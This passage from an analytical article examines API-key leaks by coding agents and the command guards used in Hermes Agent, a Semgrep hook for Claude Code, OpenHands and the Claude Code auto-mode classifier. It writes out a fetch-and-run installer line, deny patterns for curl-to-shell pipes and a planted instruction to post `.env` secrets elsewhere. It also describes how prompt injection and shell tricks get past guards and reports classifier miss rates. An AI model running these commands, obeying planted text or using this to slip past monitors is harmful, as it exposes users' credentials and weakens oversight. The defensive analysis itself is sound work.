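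Neither Lakera nor Apiiro reports testing whether the credentials worked, although one organisation told Apiiro that its key had been live. TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026) describes the credentials Lakera found as live, which is a stronger claim than Lakera's own post makes.

Most of the credential types named in the two studies are not model provider keys. Those in Apiiro's study included 379 database passwords and 23 Amazon cloud keys. Lakera found npm publishing tokens, which may be more dangerous than a provider key because a thief could use one to send malicious code to everyone who installs the package.

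Apiiro reproduced the behaviour with two current Claude models and attributed it to Claude Code rather than the models. Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, replied that Claude Code tells git to ignore the file when creating it, so people must have added the exposed copies themselves. This may explain the lower share on GitHub, but a git ignore rule doesn't necessarily keep a file out of an npm package. Cherny agreed with a reader that the same exposure could happen in auto mode, and said his team would try basic secret scanning and having auto mode catch such commands.

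### What the GitHub counts show

GitGuardian found 28.65 million new secrets in public GitHub commits in 2025. About 4 percent of them (1,275,105) were for AI services, including 113,000 keys for the model provider DeepSeek. Leaks of keys for supporting services such as search and orchestration grew five times faster than leaks of keys for the main model companies.

Some of the 81 percent rise in AI-service secrets may come from better detection. During the year, GitGuardian added many detectors for AI services, which it says can identify secrets it would previously have counted as generic. But it also reprocessed its older data with the new system, which should make the years more comparable.

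The same report gives a leak rate of 3.2 percent for commits made with Claude Code, compared with 1.5 percent for all public commits. GitGuardian identified the Claude Code commits by a line in the commit message that names Claude as co-author. They made up only 0.4 percent of the commits it scanned, so including them barely changes the 1.5 percent figure.

GitGuardian describes both rates as shares of commits that contain a secret. However, 28.65 million secrets divided by 1.94 billion commits is also about 1.5 percent, so the figures may instead be secrets per hundred commits, in which case a commit with ten keys would count ten times.

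The monthly figures suggest a smaller difference by the end of the year. Claude Code commits leaked 31 secrets per 1,000 in August, their worst month, and 13 per 1,000 in December, about the same as human commits. These figures conflict with the annual rate of 3.2 percent, because an annual average can't be higher than the August peak of 3.1 percent. GitGuardian does not explain the discrepancy.

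Even a real difference would not show that Claude Code caused more leaks. From April, its commits had about twice as many lines as human ones on average. If every line were equally likely to contain a secret, that alone would roughly double the rate per commit. People may also use Claude Code more for new projects that connect to many outside services and so need more keys. The co-author line identifies only some agent-assisted work, since developers can remove it.

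GitGuardian warns against reading the gap as simply a failure of the tool, because developers decide what to commit and can override warnings. It suggests that the release of Claude Sonnet 4.5 in late September may have contributed to the later decline. But the rate had already begun to fall after August, and Claude Code commits grew from 22 in January to 2.16 million in December, so the people using it had changed too.

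Keys also leak through the configuration files that connect agents to outside tools. GitGuardian found 24,008 secrets in configuration files for the Model Context Protocol, a standard for such connections, and confirmed that 2,117 worked. People may well have added many of these keys by hand, because the official setup guides for popular tools show keys written directly into the file.

### Why a leaked key has to be replaced

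Deleting a key from a file doesn't revoke it, so anyone who has a copy can still use it. The owner has to revoke the key with the provider and create a new one.

Copies of a leaked key are also hard to find. Git keeps earlier versions of every file, so a key stays in the project's history after a commit removes it, and other people may already have cloned or forked the repository. Lakera notes that deprecating an npm package version doesn't delete it, and advises treating any credential in a published package as compromised from the moment of publication.

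A developer's machine may also hold several copies of a key. GitGuardian analysed data that malware called Shai-Hulud 2 had collected from 6,943 machines, more than half of them automated build machines. Each working secret appeared in about eight places on the same machine, including shell settings, build output and tool caches. If an agent has read the key, a session log may contain another copy.

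Many owners leave leaked keys active for years. When GitGuardian retested secrets that it had confirmed as working in 2022, more than 64 percent still worked in January 2026. It attributes this partly to the difficulty of replacing a key that a team may use in build systems, containers and several repositories, since revoking it breaks whatever still depends on it. If the key is public, leaving it active is usually worse than breaking a build. The owner should also check the provider's usage records, since replacing the key doesn't undo any earlier misuse.

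### Redaction, scanning and spending limits

Redaction replaces a key with a placeholder before the text is displayed or stored. Dotenvx's *Redact environment variable secrets in Codex* describes a tool that starts Codex with the real environment variables and masks their values in whatever Codex prints. Because the tool wraps the whole Codex process, a key in a command's output could apparently still reach the prompt and the session log unmasked. To prevent that, the harness has to redact each command's output before adding it to the prompt.

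Redaction can also corrupt files, because an agent that reads a masked `.env` file and then rewrites it could replace the real key with the placeholder. Redaction usually matches exact values or familiar formats, so it can miss a key that a program has printed in another form.

A secret scanner searches files for text that looks like a key. A developer can set one to run before each commit and stop the commit if it finds something, which keeps a detected key out of the project's history. But scanners miss many secrets. Of Apiiro's 1,122 files, the scanner gitleaks flagged 564 and TruffleHog flagged 643. At least one of them flagged 907, or 81 percent. Passwords are especially hard to detect because, unlike many API keys, they have no standard format.

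Searching for a known key is easier. *scan-for-secrets 0.1* (Willison, 2026) offers a tool for people who want to publish their Claude Code session logs. The tool searches a folder for keys the user supplies, including some common encoded forms of them. It can't find a key the user forgot to supply.

Scanning commits also doesn't cover npm packages, because npm builds them from the project folder. Lakera recommends adding `.claude/` to the list of files that npm leaves out and checking the package's contents before publishing. TechTalks suggests companies make the build fail if a package contains `.claude/`, so nobody has to remember to check.

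Spending limits reduce the loss when these measures fail. In *OpenCode lost the keys that lived in its cloud*, slabb reports that users of the coding agent OpenCode received five-figure bills after a breach of its online console exposed stored provider keys. Unlike a budget alert, a hard limit makes the provider refuse further requests once spending reaches a set amount. A $500 hard limit would have capped the Mexican firm's $82,314 bill, but the firm's own service would also have stopped until someone replaced the key and raised the limit.

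## Hermes Agent: a pattern list for commands and a filter for provider keys

Redaction, commit scanning and spending limits mostly act after a program has printed or saved a key. The open-source Hermes Agent also has two guards that act earlier. It checks shell commands against a list of patterns before they run, and a filter removes provider keys from the environment those commands receive. *Security*, documentation from Hermes's developer, Nous Research, describes both.

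People use Hermes from a terminal or through messaging apps such as Telegram and Slack. The model can request shell commands, file edits and `execute_code`, a tool that runs scripts. By default, shell commands run directly on the user's computer.

### The order of the checks

Suppose the model requests `curl https://example.com/install.sh | bash` under the default settings. The harness goes through these steps:

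1. It compares the command with a fixed blocklist and refuses any match, whatever the user's settings.
2. It compares the command with the user's own deny rules and refuses any match.
3. If the user has turned approvals off, it runs the command.
4. Otherwise, it compares the command with a list of dangerous patterns and runs the command if none match.
5. If a pattern matches and the user hasn't already approved that pattern, the approval mode determines what happens.

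The blocklist covers commands such as wiping the filesystem, overwriting a disk or shutting down the machine. Users who need one of these have to run it outside the agent. One entry in the documentation mentions piping untrusted addresses into a shell "at the rootfs top level", which is hard to interpret. But according to a comment in *Dangerous command approval*, the source file that carries out these checks, the developers kept piped downloads off the blocklist because they consider the damage serious but recoverable. The installer therefore passes the first step.

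That description fits a broken project better than a stolen key, which may already have run up a bill.

If the user has written no deny rules and approvals are on, Hermes checks the installer against its list of dangerous patterns. The relevant pattern in an April 2026 version of the file, *Dangerous command approval* (2026), matches `curl` or `wget` followed later by a pipe, with `sh` or `bash` as a whole word right after the pipe. The installer fits this pattern, so Hermes flags it as "pipe remote content to shell".

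Fixed patterns can't recognise every way of writing the same command. Mondoo's *CVE 2026 9367* lists a flaw in the function that matches commands against Hermes Agent's patterns, with a severity score of 6.9. It says that an exploit has been publicly disclosed and that the vendor did not respond to the report. Nous Research's *Hermes Agent Security Policy* says that ways around the patterns are not security vulnerabilities, though the company welcomes reports of them as ordinary bugs.

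### What the approval modes do

| Mode | What happens to a flagged command |
|---|---|
| Smart (the default) | A second model approves it, refuses it or refers it to the user |
| Manual | Hermes asks the user |
| Off | Hermes runs it, unless the blocklist or a deny rule has already stopped it |

A user can also turn approvals off for a single session with the option `--yolo`.

In smart mode, the second model receives the command and the reason Hermes flagged it. The April version's instructions tell this model to approve commands that are clearly safe, deny those that could genuinely damage the system, and escalate if uncertain. The examples of safe commands include package installs. The examples of damage include wiped disks and dropped databases, but not stolen credentials. If the call to the second model fails, Hermes asks the user.

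For the piped installer, the second model receives neither the script nor the user's request, so its decision rests almost entirely on the web address. It can't distinguish a program the user wanted from one that a planted README suggested, and it could mistake a malicious installer on a plausible domain for a package install. The documentation gives no error rates for this model, and Nous Research may have changed the model's instructions since April.

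Manual mode avoids this problem only if the user knows something about the address. It was the default in April, and smart mode has since become the default. Users see fewer approval prompts in smart mode, so they may read each one more carefully, but they no longer see the commands that the second model approves by mistake.

The pattern list doesn't check what happens inside an `execute_code` script, which can start other programs. In sessions on messaging apps, Hermes therefore asks for approval of the whole script before running it. In a local session, it skips this approval if the user typed the request and is present to answer prompts. The script's own file and process operations then run unchecked, but any command it sends through Hermes's terminal tool is still checked against the pattern list.

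The later source file also treats terminal commands that write to the Hermes configuration file as dangerous, because the agent could otherwise turn approvals off during a session. Hermes reads the environment variable for `--yolo` only once, at startup, so a skill can't turn on `--yolo` by setting the variable later.

### Lasting approvals and unanswered prompts

When Hermes asks about a command, the user can deny it or allow it once, for the session, or always. In the April version, Hermes saves a session or permanent approval under the pattern's description, not under the command or its address. A user who approves one trusted installer for the session therefore also approves piped commands from every other server until the session ends.

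An "always" approval also applies to unattended jobs. Users can limit the risk by choosing "once" or by adding the exact text of the trusted command to the list of permanent approvals, although the script at the command's URL may still change.

Hermes can search past sessions for commands that the user often approves and suggest approving them permanently. It never suggests this for pipe-to-shell commands, however often the user has approved them. This exception is sensible because many harmless installers in the past are weak evidence that a script from the next address will be safe.

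If nobody answers a prompt within 300 seconds, Hermes denies the command. It also tells the agent not to retry on its own in the same turn. The user can still ask for the command later, which produces a new prompt.

Scheduled jobs, one-off queries and most sessions that other programs start have nobody present to approve commands. By default, Hermes immediately refuses flagged commands in these sessions, and the agent has to find another way to do the task. The owner can change the setting to approve them all, but no setting waits for a person to decide. The default may cause a legitimate job to fail, but it keeps Hermes from automatically approving a piped command that came from a stranger's text.

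### One deny rule and two commands

Deny rules let a user forbid commands that the fixed blocklist allows. Nous Research's *Running Hermes on a Personal or Work Machine* gives three examples, one of them for pipe-to-shell commands:

`*curl*|*sh*`

Each asterisk stands for any run of characters, including none, and the other characters stand for themselves. A command matches if it contains `curl`, then a pipe, then the letters `sh` anywhere after that pipe. Matching ignores case.

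The rule blocks the installer:

`curl https://example.com/install.sh | bash`

The `sh` in the address doesn't count, because it comes before the pipe. But `bash` ends in `sh`, so the command matches.

The rule also blocks this command:

`curl https://example.com/orders.json | grep shipping`

Here, `curl` downloads a list of orders and `grep` prints the lines that contain the word "shipping". Nothing in the download runs as a command. But "shipping" starts with `sh`, and the rule treats the search term like the name of a shell.

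Other harmless commands match for the same reason. Nous Research's *Hermes Agent*, a guide to answering questions about the program, suggests fetching an index of its documentation with curl. An agent that piped this index into a search for "dashboard" would trigger the rule. If a developer asked the agent to compute a downloaded script's checksum by piping it into `sha256sum`, the rule would also block that command, which is a check like the one that exposed the Codecov intrusion.

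*Tests for user-defined deny rules*, a file from the Hermes project, checks that this rule blocks a piped installer and allows a plain download. It doesn't include a harmless pipe with `sh` in it, so the tests pass despite the rule's false alarms.

When a deny rule blocks a harmless command, Hermes doesn't offer a prompt to approve it, so the user has to change the rule or run the command by hand. Hermes also tells the agent not to retry or rephrase the command because the user has explicitly forbidden it. An agent that follows this instruction can't save the orders to a file and search the file instead, even though that would be safe. A user who runs into this often may delete the rule and lose its protection against real installers.

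The built-in pattern wouldn't flag the search for "shipping", because it requires a shell's name as a whole word directly after the pipe. If it did raise a false alarm, Hermes would only have to ask the user or the second model one question. Broad patterns therefore suit commands that need approval better than commands that Hermes refuses outright.

The developers had a similar problem with their own blocklist. Its rule against deleting the whole filesystem also matched pull request titles and commit messages that mentioned the deletion command, and users could not override the block. They changed the rule to match the deletion command only where a shell would begin a new command.

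Hermes now does something similar for deny rules. It splits a line into its separate commands and compares each with the rules, so `sudo *` catches `sudo` (which runs a command with administrator rights) later in a line without matching a quoted mention of it. Splitting doesn't help with the curl rule, because neither `curl` nor `bash` is suspicious alone. The danger comes from piping one into the other, so the rule has to match the whole line. Monperrus instead proposes parsing the line as shell syntax, which preserves the connection between the commands.

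A missing pair of quotation marks could disable every deny rule. The configuration file uses YAML, a format in which an unquoted asterisk at the start of a value has a special meaning, so the file fails to parse if the user leaves `*curl*|*sh*` unquoted. According to the project's tests, Hermes lets commands past the deny rules if it can't load their configuration. Users can check a new rule by asking the agent for a harmless command that should match it.

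### Limits of matching a command's text

Nous Research warns that deny rules don't fully interpret shell commands. Hermes doesn't resolve every variable or alias in a command or inspect the scripts that a command starts, so the setup command in the 0DIN test would have passed.

An older description calls deny rules "a guardrail against an honest-but-wrong agent". An agent that obeys a planted instruction may fit that description, because it follows the instruction as part of helping its user. If the planted text contains an ordinary piped installer, as many malicious skills do, the pattern can catch it. An attacker who knows that the target uses Hermes can read the patterns in its public source code and write a command that avoids them.

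Hermes also scans project instruction files, such as `AGENTS.md`, before adding them to the prompt. It leaves out a file if it finds signs of prompt injection, such as text telling the agent to ignore earlier instructions or to send out credentials with curl. Planted text that looks like normal setup advice contains none of these signs.

### Which variables a command receives

The filter for environment variables helps if a malicious command gets past these checks. How much it removes depends on where the code runs:

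| Where the code runs | What Hermes withholds by default |
|---|---|
| Local terminal commands | Provider keys, messaging tokens and keys for Hermes's own tools |
| `execute_code` scripts | Variables with words such as KEY, TOKEN, SECRET or PASSWORD in their names, and any others without an approved prefix |
| Docker containers | All variables from the user's computer |
| Remote machines reached over SSH | All variables from the user's computer |

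A piped script that only copied its environment, like the altered Codecov uploader, would therefore not receive the provider key. This protection is useful because it doesn't depend on recognising the script as malicious.

For local terminal commands, Hermes removes only the variables it recognises as its own. A database password that the developer set for another program would apparently still reach the command. Scripts get a stricter filter, which would remove `SHOP_DB_PASSWORD` because its name contains the word PASSWORD. Using that filter for terminal commands would break many ordinary ones, such as a deployment that needs the developer's cloud credentials.

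The filter doesn't cover copies of the key on disk. Nous Research advises users to keep their keys in `~/.hermes/.env` and to make the file readable only by its owner. A piped script on the local machine runs as that owner, so it can still read the file.

Hermes's file tools block reads of project `.env` files and writes to sensitive places such as the SSH folder. These restrictions don't apply to the terminal, where `cat` can still print a protected file. Nous Research says the restrictions reduce accidental damage and give the model a clear signal to stop, but don't contain a hostile agent.

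If Hermes has no login of its own for OpenAI's Codex or Anthropic, it can use the one that Codex or Claude Code saved in the user's home directory. Users can turn this off, and Nous Research recommends doing so for reliability, because two programs that renew the same login can lock each other out. The setting doesn't hide the files from other programs.

### Why provider keys can't be exceptions

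Some skills need a secret. For example, a skill that searches for GIFs may need a key for the image service Tenor. The skill can list the environment variable that holds the secret in its description, and Hermes passes that variable to commands and scripts once the skill is loaded. Users can add other variables with the `env_passthrough` setting.

Hermes allows no exceptions for provider keys or for the tokens that connect it to messaging apps. According to Nous Research, these secrets have dedicated mechanisms. The harness calls the model, so a shell command doesn't normally need the provider key. If exceptions were allowed, a malicious skill could get the key by listing its name. Hermes also stops forwarding a variable if an add-on later declares it as a messaging credential.

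For other secrets, a user who loads a skill also agrees to share the variables it lists. A malicious skill could list a GitHub token that it doesn't need, and Hermes would pass the token on if it was set. Hermes scans skills for suspicious use of variables before installation, but the security policy describes this scan as an aid to the user's own review.

A malicious skill may not need an exception. According to the policy, skills can run Python code inside the agent's own process, where they can read any credential the agent holds in memory. Nous Research therefore says that filtering the environment "reduces casual exfiltration" but is not containment. To protect against such a skill, it relies on the user to read the skill's code before installing it.

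### Secrets in requests and output

Hermes also checks for commands that send secrets out. It flags a curl or wget request if its content includes a variable with a secret-sounding name or a credential file such as `.env`. The approval mode then applies as it does to a piped installer. Keys in an authorisation header don't trigger the check, because programs routinely authenticate to web services that way. The check covers only the command's text, so it can't catch a piped script that sends a key after it starts.

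By default, Hermes masks text in a tool's output that resembles a key, token or password before the output enters the prompt and the logs. According to the policy, a program written to get a secret past this redaction will succeed.

Hermes redacts keys from command output, but its session database stores commands as they ran, including any key typed into them. When Hermes suggests permanent approvals from this history, it masks credentials in the examples it prints and never uses a command containing one as the saved pattern. This keeps keys out of the approval list, whereas Claude Code copied them into its own.

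### Why Hermes skips command checks in containers

The policy states that "the only security boundary against an adversarial LLM is the operating system." A container provides such a boundary. When Hermes runs shell commands in a Docker container or a cloud sandbox, it doesn't check them against the fixed blocklist or the dangerous patterns, because a destructive command there can't harm the user's computer, and the user can replace a damaged container. Skipping these checks also lets the agent work without interruptions.

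This reasoning is sound for damage to the host, but it doesn't cover secrets that the user puts in the container. A task may need a GitHub token to push code. The user can list the token's environment variable in the `docker_forward_env` setting, and Hermes then copies it into the container. If the model requests a piped installer in the container, Hermes runs it without asking, even in manual mode, and the script inherits the token. Nous Research warns that code in the container can read forwarded variables and send them elsewhere.

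On the user's own computer, Hermes in manual mode would have prompted the user about the same installer. In the container, Hermes no longer prompts about suspicious commands, so one of them could steal a forwarded secret or a mounted credential file. Hermes makes the mounted file read-only, but that doesn't stop a command from reading and stealing the credentials.

User-written deny rules do apply in containers, according to the current documentation. The project's earlier tests checked that containers skipped these rules too, so older versions may lack this protection. For a user who has to forward a secret, the deny rule `*curl*|*sh*` could be worth its false alarms. Blocking the container's access to servers it doesn't need would protect the secret more reliably, because it doesn't depend on how the command is written.

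The harness calls the model from outside such a container, so the container doesn't need a provider key. Nous Research says that Hermes refuses provider keys for `env_passthrough` but doesn't mention this for `docker_forward_env`, so users can't assume that Hermes will reject a provider key there.

The container also holds only part of the agent. Shell commands and file tools run inside it, but according to the policy, `execute_code` scripts, plugins and outside tool servers still run on the user's computer. Nous Research recommends putting the entire agent in a sandbox if it reads web pages, email or other material from strangers. The agent then has to call the model from inside the sandbox, so its provider key must be there too, unless a credential proxy adds the key to outgoing requests.

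## The KTH rule: parsing a command before blocking it

Hermes Agent's example deny rule blocks a harmless search for "shipping" because the search term begins with the letters `sh`. A guard could avoid this by first identifying which words in the command are program names. Monperrus published a rule that does this and a script that applies it to each shell command before Claude Code runs it.

### From text to a syntax tree

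A text search treats a command as a row of characters. A parser applies the shell's grammar to those characters and builds a syntax tree, which records what each part of the line is and how the parts fit together. The tree for `curl URL | bash` looks like this:

- At the top is a pipeline.
  - On its left is a command with the name `curl` and one argument, the URL.
  - On its right is a command with the name `bash` and no arguments.

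The tree for `curl https://example.com/orders.json | grep shipping` has the same shape, but the command on the right is `grep`, and "shipping" is its argument. A rule that checks whether the command on the right of the pipe is a shell would let this run.

Parsing also separates commands from quoted text. Suppose a developer asks the agent to commit a change with the message "Remove curl | bash from the setup guide". The resulting `git` command contains no pipeline, because the quotation marks make the message a single argument. A text search could still flag it, as Hermes's blocklist once flagged commit messages that mentioned a deletion command.

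### The Semgrep rule

The rule runs in Semgrep, a program that developers use to search code for risky patterns. Semgrep parses a shell script into a tree and compares its patterns with that tree. The central pattern is one line:

`$FETCH ... | $SHELL`

`$FETCH` and `$SHELL` are placeholders, and the rule lists the names that can fill each one.

| Part of the pattern | What it matches |
|---|---|
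| `$FETCH` | The download programs `curl` and `wget` |
| `...` | Any options and addresses that follow the download program's name |
| The pipe | A pipe that connects the two commands |
| `$SHELL` | `bash`, `sh`, `zsh`, `dash`, `ksh`, `fish`, `csh`, `tcsh`, `ash` or `busybox` |

The last name, `busybox`, belongs to a program that combines a shell with many other small tools. The rule matches only full names, so `sh` doesn't match `sha256sum`, and an agent could compute a download's checksum in a pipeline without triggering the rule.

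Semgrep's public collection already had a rule for this danger, but Monperrus notes that it covers only `curl` piped into `bash`. He says his own rule extends to all download tools and all shells, but it lists only two tools and ten shells, so it misses commands that use any other program to download or run the text.

### How the hook blocks a command

Semgrep only reports matches, so another program has to stop the command. Monperrus uses a hook, a user-supplied program that Claude Code calls before an action and that can block it. If the model requests a piped installer, the hook should work as follows:

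1. Claude Code pauses the request and sends the hook a description of it in JSON, a structured text format.
2. The hook extracts the command with a small program called jq. If it finds no command, it exits without objecting.
3. The hook writes the command to a temporary file and runs Semgrep on that file.
4. If Semgrep finds no match, the hook exits silently. Otherwise, it prints a decision to block the command and a reason.
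5. Claude Code reads the decision, cancels the command and shows the model the reason.

When the hook exits silently, Anthropic says the command still goes through the normal permission checks, so the hook can refuse a command but never removes a permission prompt.

The reason given for the block includes instructions to download the script, inspect it and then run it, so the agent can still complete a legitimate installation. Hermes, by contrast, instructs the agent not to rephrase a command that matches a deny rule.

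The published script may no longer block anything when Semgrep is working. Semgrep prints its findings to standard output by default, according to its *CLI reference*, and the hook prints its decision there too. According to Anthropic's current documentation, Claude Code can't read the decision if the output contains any other text. The hook discards Semgrep's error messages but not its findings, so a match would apparently prevent the hook from blocking the command.

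Monperrus reports that the hook did block matching commands. Claude Code may have changed since June, or the script he tested may have differed from the published one. The fix is simple because the hook needs only Semgrep's exit code, the number a program returns when it finishes, and can discard the printed findings. A developer who installs the hook should also check that Claude Code refuses to run a harmless piped script.

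### When part of the hook fails

If Semgrep is missing, the hook blocks every shell command, even `echo hello`. The hook allows a command only when Semgrep returns an exit code of zero, which means it ran successfully and found no match. It treats any other code as a match, including the one the shell returns when it can't find Semgrep.

The hook also hides the error message that would explain the problem. The agent would see only a message that piping downloads into a shell is forbidden, even if it had tried to list a folder. An invalid rule file would have the same effect, since Semgrep returns a nonzero code then too.

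Blocking everything is inconvenient, but the developer will soon notice it. Several other failures leave the agent working without the guard:

| What fails | What happens to the command |
|---|---|
| Semgrep is missing or its rule file is invalid | The hook blocks it |
| jq is missing | The hook finds no command to check and lets it continue |
| The hook script is missing | Claude Code shows an error notice and lets it continue |
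| The hook takes longer than its 15-second limit | Claude Code cancels the hook and lets the command continue |

The missing jq is the hardest to notice because the hook exits as if it had succeeded. Anthropic says error messages from a successful hook appear only in debug logs.

Since version 2.1.295, Claude Code has had an `onFailure` setting that can block a command when the hook crashes, doesn't start or times out. Monperrus's settings don't use it. The setting wouldn't help if jq were missing, because Claude Code wouldn't detect a failure, so the script would have to check for jq itself.

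The hook has other gaps. Semgrep reports invalid syntax through its exit code only in a strict mode that the hook doesn't use, so the hook may treat a command that Semgrep can't parse as harmless. On Windows machines without Git Bash, Claude Code runs commands in PowerShell, and a hook registered only for the Bash tool never starts. Anthropic's documentation also implies that a project's settings can turn off a user's own hooks, but not hooks that an administrator deploys in managed settings. An organisation that depends on such a hook should therefore deploy it in managed settings.

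### The seven-command test

Monperrus tested the hook on seven commands. It blocked all five that piped a download into a shell. Three of those used `curl`, one each with `bash`, `sh` and `zsh`, and two used `wget` with `bash`. The hook allowed the two harmless commands, one that saved an installer to a file and one that printed "hello".

A fixed rule always gives the same answer for the same command, so this test didn't need the hundreds of repetitions that researchers use for models. The test shows that the rule recognises the ordinary form of a piped installer. But its five commands covered only three of the ten listed shells, and Monperrus somewhat overstates their coverage by describing them as all the major variants.

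The test also can't show that parsing works better than a text search. Neither harmless command contains a pipe, so neither could cause the kind of false alarm that parsing is meant to prevent. A text pattern matching either download program, then a pipe, then one of the three shells would have classified all seven commands correctly.

A more informative test would run the rule on thousands of commands from real agent sessions and count how many harmless ones it blocks. Running it on installer lines from public projects would show how many dangerous commands it misses. The test could also measure the delay from starting Semgrep for every command. Monperrus calls the hook "low-overhead" but gives no timings.

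### Saving the script before running it

The rule lets an agent save a script with one command and run it with another. Monperrus presents this as the hook's main limit, although the hook's message recommends the same two steps with an inspection between them.

Saving the script leaves a file that the agent can read before running it and the developer can examine later. However, saving a malicious script doesn't make it safe, and the hook can't ensure that anyone reads it. The hook checks each command separately, so when the agent runs the file, the hook has no record that it came from the internet.

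A harness could keep such a record and ask the user before running any downloaded file. But it would also ask about every legitimate installer, and the user would still have to judge the script. If the agent inspects the script instead, the script's text enters the prompt, and a comment addressed to the model could work as another planted instruction. The script may also fetch more text when it runs, as the script in the 0DIN test did.

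### What a checksum adds

Once the script is on disk, the developer or the agent can compare its checksum with the publisher's. A match shows that the file is identical to the one the publisher used, because there is no known practical way to write a different script with the same checksum.

Comparing checksums exposed the altered Codecov script, but it doesn't help if the attacker controls both the script and the checksum. Someone who plants a README with a malicious installer line can also publish a correct checksum for the script. An agent that compares the two will find that they match, and might wrongly conclude that the script is safe. Even a checksum from an honest source doesn't cover anything the script downloads after it starts.

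A developer can avoid depending on the publisher by reading the script once and recording its checksum in their own project. Later installations can stop if the downloaded file differs from the version the developer read. Plugin marketplaces pin reviewed commits for the same reason. But every legitimate update also changes the checksum, so someone has to read the new version before installations can continue.

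### OpenHands: a risk rating and a separate decision

The KTH hook both recognises a dangerous command and blocks it. OpenHands, an open-source coding agent, can separate these two jobs. Its *Security & Action Confirmation* describes rule-based analyzers that rate each action's risk and a confirmation policy that determines whether to ask the user.

One OpenHands analyzer looks for known dangerous text. Another looks for dangerous combinations, such as a download piped into a program that runs it, and requires both parts to appear in the same field of the request. A third takes the highest rating the others give. The possible ratings are low, medium, high and unknown. Under the recommended policy, OpenHands asks before running actions rated high or unknown and runs the rest without asking. A developer has to configure both the analyzer and the policy, because an analyzer alone doesn't change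 when OpenHands asks.

The analyzers search for shell patterns only in the parts of a request that can run. If the model mentions a deletion command in its reasoning but requests a harmless file listing, the analyzers don't flag the listing. This prevents some false alarms without a full parser, but it doesn't solve the problem of quoted text inside a command.

OpenHands summarises its approach as "Confirm, don't block." A false alarm only results in a question, as with Hermes's approval patterns. If no answer arrives, OpenHands' example program rejects the action.

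OpenHands says the analyzers are not a full shell parser, a complete defence against prompt injection or a replacement for a sandbox, and that they may miss threats outside their patterns. They can't block an action by themselves, so OpenHands suggests using hooks for that. Software that calls a tool directly bypasses them, and they don't check some text, including the end of very long inputs. OpenHands recommends using them with Docker containers.

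### Commands that the shell rewrites

*GuardFall*, a June 2026 survey by Adversa AI, reports that attackers could get commands past the guards of ten of eleven open-source agents because a shell rewrites text before running it. The exception was Continue, which parses commands first.

The ten included Hermes. Five of them had a guard that inspected commands, three relied on the user to approve each command, and two relied on a sandbox that the user could turn off. One of those two was OpenHands, whose pattern analyzer is off by default, according to Adversa AI. The result therefore shows how often a planted command could reach the shell in some common configuration, not how well ten pattern lists performed.

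SecurityWeek's *Decades-Old Bash Tricks Expose AI Coding Agents to Supply Chain Attacks* points out that an attack also needs a model that follows the planted text, and either automatic approval or a disabled sandbox.

Parsing isn't enough if the guard then compares only the original text of each part. Adversa AI found this weakness in one agent that built a syntax tree. The KTH rule may have the same weakness, since it also compares names as they appear in the tree, but the survey did not test that rule.

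Continue prompts the user for approval when it can't determine from a command's text what the shell will run. It also prompts for any pipeline that ends in a shell. As a result, developers have to approve several harmless commands in a typical session, and Adversa AI says such interruptions lead people to turn on automatic approval.

In its default mode, Continue blocked or asked about all 24 commands in a live test. When its command-line version was set to approve commands automatically, 18 of the 24 ran or would have run, because that mode skips the questions and blocks only commands that Continue forbids outright.

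## Claude Code auto mode: a model that judges each command

Anthropic built Claude Code's auto mode for people who are tired of approval prompts like Continue's. A second model, the classifier, reviews the agent's riskier actions in the user's place. Unlike the KTH rule, which compares a command with a fixed pattern, the classifier judges whether the command breaks one of its plain-English rules, given what the user asked for.

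### The order of decisions

According to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, Claude Code takes each action through these steps and stops at the first one that settles it:

1. It applies the user's own rules. A deny rule blocks the action, an ask rule produces a permission prompt, and an allow rule lets the action run.
2. It approves actions that only read, and edits to files in the working folder.
3. It sends almost everything else to the classifier, including most shell commands and network requests.
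4. If the classifier blocks the action, Claude receives the reason, usually the name of the rule, and can look for another way to do the task.

One exception is that Claude Code asks the user the first time Claude's file tools try to read outside the working folder. It also suspends allow rules broad enough to permit any shell command or any Python script, because they would let the riskiest commands skip the classifier. Narrow rules, such as one that allows `npm test`, stay active. Anthropic warns that a narrow rule can still let a destructive argument through unreviewed, and offers a setting that suspends all allow rules for shell commands.

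If the classifier blocks three actions in a row, or 20 in one session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. Auto mode resumes once the user approves the action in the prompt. Users can't change either number.

A run with the `-p` option usually has nobody to ask for approval. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, when auto mode launched in March 2026, Claude Code ended such a run once it reached the limit. According to the current documentation, the blocked action doesn't run but Claude keeps working, so an unattended agent can try other commands.

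When a review produces no verdict, Claude Code blocks the action. The KTH hook does the opposite if it runs out of time.

### What the classifier receives

The classifier receives the user's messages, the agent's tool calls except simple lookups, and `CLAUDE.md`, the project's instruction file. Claude Code removes the results of the tool calls, and the March design also removed the agent's explanations.

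In Anthropic's example, a file tells the agent to post the contents of `.env` to some address "for validation", and the agent obeys. The classifier never receives the file, so the planted text can't influence it. It receives only a request that would send secrets to an outside server, which the user never asked for. Leaving out the agent's explanations has a similar purpose, since an agent that has convinced itself to take a bad action could otherwise convince the classifier to allow it.

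The classifier can't read a script that the agent has downloaded, but it does receive the earlier commands. If the agent saves an installer with one command and runs it with the next, the classifier can connect the two, which the KTH hook can't do.

Claude Code ignores auto mode rules in a project's settings files, because a repository could otherwise include its own exceptions. But it still passes the project's `CLAUDE.md` to the classifier, and the documentation doesn't cover how the classifier treats a malicious one.

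Anthropic's description of what the classifier receives, which leaves out tool results, applies only to requests that Claude Code itself sends. In newer versions, Anthropic's server can review actions as part of the session's ordinary model requests. The documentation of that review does not state that tool results are left out.

A separate check scans tool results for signs of prompt injection and, if it finds any, adds a warning before the agent receives them. An attacker who plants instructions therefore has to get past this scan, persuade the agent, and get the resulting command accepted by the classifier, which does not receive the instructions.

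### Error rates at launch

The classifier that Anthropic described in March works in two stages. The first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. The second runs only on actions that the first has flagged, and reasons about them before deciding. Anthropic published the errors of the first stage alone and of the two together:

| What Anthropic measured | First stage alone | Both stages |
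|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked, among 10,000 real tool calls by its employees | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Dangerous actions missed, among 52 from real sessions | 6.6% | 17% |
| Exfiltration attempts missed, among 1,000 synthetic ones | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most of the false alarms, but it lets through some dangerous actions that the first stage caught. Anthropic accepted this because a tool that blocked one in 12 harmless actions would be frustrating to use.

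The 52 dangerous actions came from sessions in which Claude did more than its user wanted, with no attacker involved. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated the action as approved by the user. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" hasn't agreed to let Claude overwrite the project's history on the server.

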